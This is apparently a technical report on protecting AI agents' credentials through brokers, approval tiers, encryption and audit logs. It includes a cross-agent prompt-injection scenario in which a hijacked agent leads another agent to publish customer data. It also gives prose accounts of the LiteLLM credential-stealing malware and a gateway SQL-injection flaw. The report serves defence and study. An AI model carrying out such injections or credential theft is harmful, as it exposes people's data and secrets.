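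Even when each agent has narrow rights, a hijacked agent may be able to exploit another agent's rights. Suppose a support agent can read customer records and comment on internal tickets, while a release-notes agent can read tickets and publish a public page. Neither agent can both read customer records and publish. But a hijacked support agent could copy a record into a ticket and add an instruction to include it in the next release notes. If the release-notes agent followed the instruction, it would publish the record without either agent breaking its rules.

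Hartman rates this as a high-severity threat and proposes looking for suspicious patterns across agents. He gives no test results, however, and acknowledges that a new system needs time to learn what is normal. A simpler precaution is to map which agents can write to places that others read. If two agents are connected like this, the builder should ask whether one agent could safely have both sets of permissions. If not, it's better to break the connection or put a person between them.

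When one agent starts another, the second should get no more permissions than the first. Anthropic's auto mode also checks the task the first agent hands over, because the second agent's classifier would otherwise treat it as a user's request. Auto mode checks again when the second agent returns its work, in case that agent read something hostile, but a problem found then only adds a warning.

### Three tiers of approval

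Hartman sorts requests into three tiers:

| Tier | Requests | How approval works | Example for a coding agent |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Low-risk, already authorised and normal for this agent | Automatic, in under 10 milliseconds | Open a pull request |
| 2 | Moderate risk, or unusual for this agent | A person gets a notification, and the request fails if nobody answers within five minutes | Change a build workflow |
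| 3 | High-risk, destructive or administrative | The request waits while a person approves it with a security key or passkey | Delete a release |

Approval requests should go to the agent's owner or the team that runs the service, since someone handling a general approval queue may not know what the agent is for. If the approval system goes down, tier 1 requests continue and the others fail. Hartman also requires signed approvals so that an attacker can't forge one.

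A compromised agent may try to disguise a risky request as a tier 1 request, so the tier should depend on the parsed action and resource, and never on a description or risk level that the agent provides.

### What the approver needs to see

Hartman's tier 2 screen shows the agent's identity, the action, its scope and the justification. Those details would not have been enough to catch the invoice file, because the problem was in the earlier steps.

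Hossain and colleagues tested four screens on 80 volunteers, who made 960 decisions. Half of the requests violated the user's instructions. The screens ranged from a short description of the action to a version that linked the request to its history:

| Screen | Harmful requests approved | Legitimate requests approved | Median time |
|---|---|---|---|
| Short description | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16.3 s |
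| Exact tool arguments as well | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23.4 s |
| User's instructions and a full log as well | 32.5% | 87.5% | 38.6 s |
| The same facts, linked into one statement of the consequence | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33.2 s |

Most of the improvement came from showing reviewers more information. The linked version did better than the plain log, but the study was too small to rule out chance. The linked version made no difference for violations that depended on a chain of steps, where reviewers approved seven of 30 requests with either version.

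For the workflow change, the approver should see Alice's original assignment, the exact lines that would change, and the consequence, such as "this build can read the deployment key". The intermediary has to produce all of this from its own records. It should also tie the approval to that exact request and ask again if the request changes. *Let the Agent Do It?* suggests showing whether the action is reversible, which would help people decide where to focus.

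Without such details, approval can offer little protection. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) analyses 290 reports of agent misuse and finds that weak user review contributed to 105. In 31, the approval prompt didn't make the effects clear. For example, a prompt to run `python3 setup.py` doesn't show what the script will do. In 80, the user had switched on automatic approval, often to avoid hundreds of prompts.

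### How well people and classifiers catch harmful requests

Anthropic ran the largest test of people's attention to permission prompts. It hired 1,053 testers for a coding study and replaced one prompt in each session with a clearly dangerous command. The testers refused it 13.6% of the time overall, with the rate falling from about 17% early in a session to about 5% after 50 or more prompts. Auto mode blocked 89% of the same commands.

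The testers worked in an artificial environment with nothing of their own at risk, so they may have been less careful than usual. Anthropic also has an interest in the result, since it was making auto mode the default. But real users approve 97% of Claude Code's permission prompts, which suggests many don't read them closely.

Having a person review the commands the classifier allowed would have helped very little in this study. The classifier blocked 937 of the 1,053 commands, and the testers caught only six of the rest. Using both would have stopped 943, or 89.6%.

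Classifiers also make mistakes. An earlier version of auto mode missed 17% of 52 real actions that went beyond the user's request. When it missed one, it had usually detected the danger but wrongly treated something the user had said as permission. It blocked only 0.4% of ordinary actions. Anthropic still recommends human review for high-stakes changes to production systems.

Developers who carefully review their agents' code don't necessarily review their agents' actions as carefully. Wu, Wermke and colleagues (2026) surveyed 203 developers for *From Delegation to Action Approval*. Of those who carefully reviewed most or all of their agents' code, 61% often approved at least one type of action without close review, compared with 67% of the others, a difference that could easily be due to chance. Developers who knew of a security incident or worrying practice involving agents were more likely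 to approve actions without close review, perhaps because they gave their agents more freedom.

Having users write their own permission rules may not help. In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, Yan (2026) had 113 people from outside the software industry supervise a simulated assistant that took 11 necessary actions and seven that nobody had requested. Participants who decided on each action individually blocked 59.6% of the unrequested ones, while those who first set "allow", "ask" or "never" rules for spending, sending, deleting and reading private data blocked 39.6%.

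The rule-writers chose "ask" for 114 of 140 rules, then approved two-thirds of the unrequested actions they were asked about. Some of those actions were mild, such as calling the airport to confirm a flight, and the rule-writers may have welcomed them. Still, "ask" is less cautious than it looks, because people often approve the action anyway. For the billing agent, the operator should decide as many cases as possible in advance and save "ask" for the few where a person has something specific to check.

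Hartman proposes several ways to reduce approval fatigue: limiting how many approval requests an agent can send, requiring a break after a run of approvals, flagging changes in the pattern of requests, and occasionally presenting a harmless request as suspicious to test the approver. Limiting requests seems most promising, given how quickly Anthropic's testers stopped paying attention. The tests could backfire if approvers learn that alarming messages are usually drills. A planted harmful request that the system can't execute, like the one in Anthropic's study, would give a more useful measurement.

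Repeated approvals also shouldn't automatically become a permanent permission. *Let the Agent Do It?* points out that they may come from tiredness or a deadline rather than growing trust.

### Signs of failure

- **The agent can choose its own rules.** Pogorelec (2026), in *AI Agent Gateway*, describes an open-source product from Tuskira that checks every tool call against a profile. If the operator hasn't tied an agent's key to a profile, the caller can name any profile in a header. The header test for agent names, described earlier, would reveal this too.
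- **A forbidden action works another way.** Try to merge by pushing to `main` or by using GraphQL.
- **The log contains no refusals after weeks of use.** The rules may be fine, but they may also be so broad that they never apply.
- **Approvals take two or three seconds.** The volunteers in the study by Hossain and colleagues needed a median of 16 seconds even for a short description.
- **An old approval covers a new request.** Approve one request, change a single parameter and send it again. The intermediary should ask a second time.
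- **The service lists a key, webhook or collaborator that nobody remembers adding.** Revoke it first, then search the intermediary's log for the request that created it.

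## Protecting the intermediary that holds the credentials

An attacker who compromises the intermediary can use every credential it stores, and limits on what a hijacked agent can ask the intermediary to do don't prevent this. Posta, who argues for proxying, concedes, "We just created a high-value target." Of the eleven threats in Hartman's draft, only compromise of the broker is rated critical. Hartman's main example of such a compromise is the March 2026 attack on LiteLLM.

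### The LiteLLM compromise

LiteLLM is open-source software that gives programs one interface to many AI providers. Developers can install it as a library or run it as a gateway, an intermediary mostly for calls to language models. The gateway stores the provider keys and gives users separate keys.

The attack began with Trivy, a vulnerability scanner that attackers had already compromised. LiteLLM's build system ran Trivy without pinning its version. All the build steps shared one environment, which contained long-lived credentials for publishing releases. Dholakia and Jaff (2026) conclude in *Security Townhall Updates*, the company's account of the attack, that the malicious scanner read the credentials from that environment.

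On 24 March the attackers uploaded LiteLLM version 1.82.7 directly to PyPI, the main registry for Python packages, and 1.82.8 soon afterwards. The malware was not in the public source code, so reviewing that code would not have revealed it. Anyone who installed LiteLLM without specifying a version, or installed another package that depended on it, could receive the malware. According to LiteLLM's *Security Update* (2026), the malware searched for environment variables, SSH keys, cloud credentials, Kubernetes tokens and database passwords, then sent them to a domain that resembled LiteLLM's own. It could also spread through Kubernetes clusters and install backdoors, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *TeamPCP Expands Supply Chain Campaign With LiteLLM PyPI Compromise* (2026), so removing the package might not have been enough.

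LiteLLM says the packages were available for about 40 minutes. PyPI's *Incident Report* (2026) says they were quarantined 2 hours and 32 minutes after upload and downloaded more than 119,000 times. PyPI's time seems more likely, because 119,000 downloads in 40 minutes would be nearly 3,000 a minute, and the package averages about 1,700. InfoQ's *PyPI Supply Chain Attack Compromises LiteLLM, Enabling the Exfiltration of Sensitive Information* (2026) gave an early count of just over 40,000 downloads. Neither count is the number of victims, since one build system can download a package many times.

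The amount stolen is much less certain. Hartman gives estimates of over 300 GB of compressed credentials and about 500,000 corporate identities, but these cover the attackers' whole campaign, which included other software. A BleepingComputer report reposted by Fixed Intel also gives a figure of 500,000, but for data thefts, many of them duplicates, and BleepingComputer could not confirm it.

One confirmed victim is Mercor, which supplies training data to AI companies. Mercor told Fortune that it was "one of thousands of companies" affected (Nolan, 2026, *Mercor, a $10 billion AI startup that works with companies including OpenAI*). The extortion group Lapsus$ claimed to have taken up to four terabytes of data from Mercor, though Smalley describes the claim as hundreds of gigabytes (*Mercor confirms security incident tied to LiteLLM supply chain attack*). Mercor did not answer questions about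 the claim, and nobody has publicly established how Lapsus$ got the data.

### Which lessons apply to other intermediaries

The attack only partly supports Hartman's reading of it as a warning about keeping many keys in one process. LiteLLM's official container image for the gateway was unaffected because its dependencies had fixed versions, and LiteLLM's hosted service was also unaffected. The malware collected whatever credentials it found on the machines that installed it, including developers' own, and the intermediary design is meant to remove such scattered keys. However, a company that had built its own gateway image that morning could have lost its provider keys too.

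An attack in April is a better example of the danger to a central store. *CVE-2026-42208* (Clark, 2026) describes a flaw in how the LiteLLM gateway checked keys. The gateway put the caller's key directly into a database query, so a stranger could add commands to the query without authenticating. Clark's team at Sysdig, a security company, recorded the first attack about 36 hours after the flaw appeared in GitHub's global advisory database. The attacker went directly to the tables that held users' keys, provider credentials and the gateway's settings. SecurityWeek's *Fresh LiteLLM Vulnerability Exploited Shortly After Disclosure* refers to extracted keys that nobody had abused, but Clark reports no confirmed theft.

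Version 1.82.6, which LiteLLM had recommended as safe in March, contained the April flaw. Pinning a version blocks malicious updates, but also security patches. PyPI recommends lock files with checksums, a delay of perhaps three days before installing new releases, and a separate process for installing security fixes sooner. Even a one-day delay would have avoided the March packages.

Any intermediary can have a poisoned dependency or a flaw in the code that reads requests. Its builder should therefore separate the build steps, use short-lived publishing credentials and keep the service off the public internet. The intermediary also needs its own egress control, limiting it to the approved services and its own components. Malware inside it then can't send the keys directly to a new domain, although it might still use an account at an approved service.

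### Separating the decision from the credential

In Hartman's scheme, the credential delivery point fetches a credential only after checking the policy decision point's signed approval. Keeping the two apart limits what an attacker gains by taking over just one component:

| Component taken over | What the attacker gains | What remains protected |
|---|---|---|
| Agent | The use of permitted requests | The credentials themselves |
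| Identity service on one machine | The identities of that machine's agents | Requests outside those agents' rules |
| Policy decision point | The power to approve forbidden requests | The credentials themselves |
| Credential delivery point | Every credential it can fetch | The records in a separate log |
| Copy of the credential database | Encrypted records | Their contents, if the key is elsewhere |
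| Audit log | A chance to hide evidence | The credentials and the rules |

The second and third rows depend on details. Anyone who steals an agent's identity can use everything the rules approve automatically. Hartman expects that a compromised decision point cannot approve requests that need a person's approval, but this holds only if the delivery point checks the person's signature itself. Otherwise the decision point could sign a false statement that someone had approved the request.

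The separation also does less to contain a compromised delivery point, which has standing access to the vault. Hartman doesn't require the vault to check for an approval before releasing a credential, so malicious code in the delivery point could skip the decision. The vault's own access limits are then the main protection. In Hartman's smallest deployment, one program handles both delivery and vault access, and everything runs on the same machine.

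The two components also need separate administrators and, where practical, different dependencies, because a poisoned package installed on both would have let the attacker compromise both.

### Encrypting credentials under a key held elsewhere

Hartman recommends a vault backed by a hardware security module, a device that uses cryptographic keys without releasing them. This works well for signing keys, but a bearer credential has to leave the device because it must be sent to the service. The module can protect the master key that encrypts the credentials, but it can't detect whether an authorised program requesting decryption has been hijacked.

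Posta describes how Solo's commercial gateway uses envelope encryption, which puts two layers around each credential:

```
stored token    = encrypt(data key, token)
stored data key = encrypt(master key, data key; owner, resource)
```

The controller, which manages the token store, creates a new data key every time it saves a token. It encrypts the token with the data key and has the data key encrypted with the master key. Each encrypted token is tied to an owner, recorded as a keyed hash of the user's ID, and a resource, such as the code host. Neither value is secret, but decryption fails if either is wrong, so nobody can pass off Bob's record as Alice's.

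How much this helps depends on where the master key is and who can use it:

| Arrangement | What a compromised controller can read |
|---|---|
| Master key in a Kubernetes Secret | Every credential, offline and without a record |
| Master key in Amazon's Key Management Service (KMS), with standing permission to decrypt | Every credential while the attacker has access, with a log entry for each |
| Master key in KMS, with a separate grant for each decryption | Credentials that current requests need |

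A stolen database alone reveals nothing in any of these arrangements. Posta advises against the first outside simple demonstrations, because a cluster administrator or anyone who steals a cluster backup can obtain the master key. The second lets the operator detect bulk theft and withdraw permission, but an attacker may finish copying the store before anyone responds.

The third takes away the controller's standing permission. When Alice's agent contacts the code host:

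1. The gateway checks Alice's login token and signs a single-use proof that names her and the code host. The proof expires in about 30 seconds.
2. The controller finds Alice's encrypted record and sends the login token and the proof to a separate grant broker.
3. The grant broker verifies both, applies its rules and calculates the owner value from the login token.
4. It asks KMS for a temporary grant that lets the controller decrypt only data with that owner and resource.
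5. KMS checks those values and returns the data key. The controller decrypts Alice's token and passes it to the gateway.
6. The gateway adds the token to the request, and the grant broker cancels the grant.

The grant broker has no database and can't decrypt anything. Amazon's permissions let the broker create grants only for the controller. An attacker who compromised both the controller and the grant broker could read the whole store, as in the second arrangement.

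Posta says that neither component alone can read a credential. That is slightly too strong, because the controller handles Alice's token in plain text whenever she needs it. If the store holds tokens for 1,000 users and 200 of them use an agent on a given day, an attacker in the controller could collect about 200 users' tokens that day. These would work elsewhere until they expired or were revoked. A compromised gateway may be worse, because it has the users' login tokens and signs the proofs. It could request Alice's other credentials too, unless the broker's rules stopped it.

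A reviewer can test this arrangement by calling KMS with the controller's identity and no grant, then by using Alice's grant on Bob's record. Both attempts should fail. The arrangement depends on stable user IDs. If the company changes login systems and Alice's ID changes, her stored tokens won't decrypt until she authorises access again.

### Clearing memory, isolating customers and keeping a separate log

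Hartman requires the delivery point to erase a long-lived credential from memory immediately after use. This protects against an attacker who gains access later, but not one who is already watching the process. Hartman calls the remaining exposure "irreducible" for minting, which needs the credential only when it issues a token. A proxy needs the credential for every request, so on a busy service it may almost always be in memory.

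Caching credentials makes this worse. According to Docker, its cache lasts 55 minutes by default, but the setting `--refresh on-demand` replaces it with a fresh lookup for each use. This would suit a powerful credential that agents seldom use. Docker normally stores secrets in the operating system's keychain, but on a Linux machine without one, it falls back to a file protected only by file permissions. Any program running under the same user account can read that file, so the agent must run outside that account.

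Isolation limits how many credentials one break-in exposes. Docker's service secrets are available to all sandboxes by default, but the user can restrict each secret to a single sandbox. *Caging the Agents* uses a separate sidecar for each agent, so an attacker who takes over one sidecar gets only that agent's keys. But the sidecars get their keys from Kubernetes Secrets, so someone with broad access to the cluster could still collect every agent's keys.

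A hosted intermediary adds the risk that one customer, or an attacker who compromises the provider, will reach other customers' credentials. Hartman requires separate policy engines and vaults for each customer. Kenney and colleagues cite a June 2024 disclosure by Hugging Face, which hosts AI models and applications, that it had detected unauthorised access to secrets stored for those applications. It advised affected users to replace them. The incident shows why customers need a quick way to replace all their keys, although the disclosure doesn't establish that the attacker took every secret. A separate master key for each customer would also help, as long as the provider's software can't use all of them at once.

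Neither the decision point nor the delivery point can change old entries in Hartman's audit log, so an attacker would need to compromise the log as well as the broker to alter them. But a hijacked delivery point can stop reporting what it does. The operator therefore needs records from systems the delivery point doesn't control, such as KMS and the services. A decryption in the KMS log with no matching agent request should trigger an immediate alert. Posta also suggests planting canary credentials in the store and raising an alarm when decryptions suddenly increase.

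### What happens when a component fails

A component that can't do its job should stop requests, not let them through unchecked. Hartman specifies this for each part of the broker:

| Unavailable component | What stops | What continues |
|---|---|---|
| Policy decision point | All new credential requests, because nothing can check the rules | No new requests |
| Credential delivery point | All new credentials | No new credentials |
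| Vault | All new credentials, because the stored ones are unreachable | No new credentials |
| Audit log | All new credentials, because nothing can record their use | No new credentials |
| Approval service | Requests that need a person | Low-risk requests with automatic approval |
| SPIRE, the identity service | New agent sessions | Existing sessions until their certificates expire, an hour by default |

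With minting, agents can also continue to use unexpired tokens. With a proxy, they stop immediately.

Hartman describes "break-glass" access for emergencies. Two people must authorise it together, and it expires after 30 minutes by default. It bypasses the decision point but is still recorded in the audit log, and the organisation must review it afterwards.

Emergency access would help if the decision point failed or a bad rule blocked urgent work. It wouldn't help if the vault were down, because the credential would still be out of reach, and a log outage would seem to rule it out too. The draft doesn't specify how the delivery point, which normally accepts only decisions signed by the decision point, recognises an emergency approval. The emergency path needs at least as much protection as the normal one. A token issued in the 29th minute could outlast the emergency access by an hour, so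 the builder should limit each emergency token's lifetime to the time remaining.

Hartman's minimum installation does not include break-glass (emergency) access, which requires two approvals that one person with a laptop can't provide. Hartman warns that people under pressure may create undocumented ways around a system that refuses requests. A developer with a production outage and no emergency procedure may well paste a real key into the sandbox. Operators should rehearse the emergency procedure, then check that the access has ended.

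### Delay and availability

There is little published evidence on how much an intermediary slows an agent down:

| Figure | What it covers | How firm it is |
|---|---|---|
| 2 to 5 ms | Extra time to open a connection from a sandbox, in *Caging the Agents* | Approximate, for a sandbox the fleet had not yet moved to |
| 500 to 3,000 ms | A language model's response, also in *Caging the Agents* | Approximate |
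| Under 10 ms | Automatic approval in Hartman's draft | A specification, not a measurement |
| No figure | A separate KMS grant for each decryption | Posta acknowledges that it adds delay |

None of these measures the time a credential proxy adds. Anthropic's reported speedup came from starting fewer containers, so it doesn't fill the gap.

The grant arrangement needs three calls before the controller can read a token: one to the grant broker, one from the broker to KMS, and one from the controller to KMS. If each took 20 ms, the total would be 60 ms, or 2% to 12% of the model response times above. One slow component can delay the whole chain, so the builder should measure the slowest 1% of requests as well as the median. Posta warns that KMS grants stop scaling at some point and has designed a variant for larger systems.

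Availability also falls when every request depends on several components. If five components each work 99.9% of the time and fail independently, all five work at once 0.999⁵ ≈ 99.5% of the time, which means about 3.6 hours of downtime in a 30-day month, compared with 43 minutes for one component. Backup copies reduce the downtime, but each copy is another machine to protect. None of these sources reports the uptime of a working credential broker.

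### Whether the design only moves the risk

The design still stores credentials, but it moves them from the agent to an intermediary, which can be much safer. An agent reads text from strangers, runs code it has just written and may install packages, while an intermediary can be a small program that does none of these things. Gathering scattered keys, like those in the healthcare fleet's start-up and configuration files, into one guarded store seems clearly worthwhile.

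The risk of a leak also depends on how many copies of a key exist. Suppose nine agents hold the same code-host key, and each has a 5% chance of leaking it in a year. If the leaks are independent, the chance that at least one agent leaks the key that year is 1 − 0.95⁹, or about 37%. If only a single store held the key, and it was guarded no better than an agent, the chance would be 5%.

The comparison is closer when each agent has a different key. If each of 200 agents has a 2% chance of a leak each year, an average of four keys leak a year. A store holding all 200 keys, with a 1% chance of a break-in each year, would lose an average of two a year, but a break-in would expose all 200 at once. An organisation that could cope with losing four keys but not 200 might reasonably prefer to keep the keys apart. But the leaks may not be independent. The LiteLLM malware could take different keys from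 thousands of machines on the same morning because the machines had all installed the same package.

A central store also makes recovery easier, because the operator has a list of what to replace. After the LiteLLM attack, affected users had to treat every credential on a machine as stolen, including any they had forgotten about.

Concentrating credentials in one store increases the risk in some cases. If the store runs beside the agents and its master key is in the same cluster, a single break-in could expose every credential. If the old copies remain in use, the organisation has the risks of both the copies and the store. A store can also increase exposure by replacing narrow one-hour tokens with permanent keys, or by collecting tokens from employees who never use agents. A small team that can't patch a gateway within a day or so may be safer with a well-run hosted service, or with a few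 short-lived tokens and no gateway.

Keys can also be split among several stores, as a middle option between one store and hundreds of copies. Ten stores of 20 keys would expose as many keys on average as one store of 200, if each were as hard to break into as the single store, but one break-in would expose only 20 keys. This works only if the stores have separate master keys and administrators. Keys that can deploy software or move money are good candidates for a store of their own.
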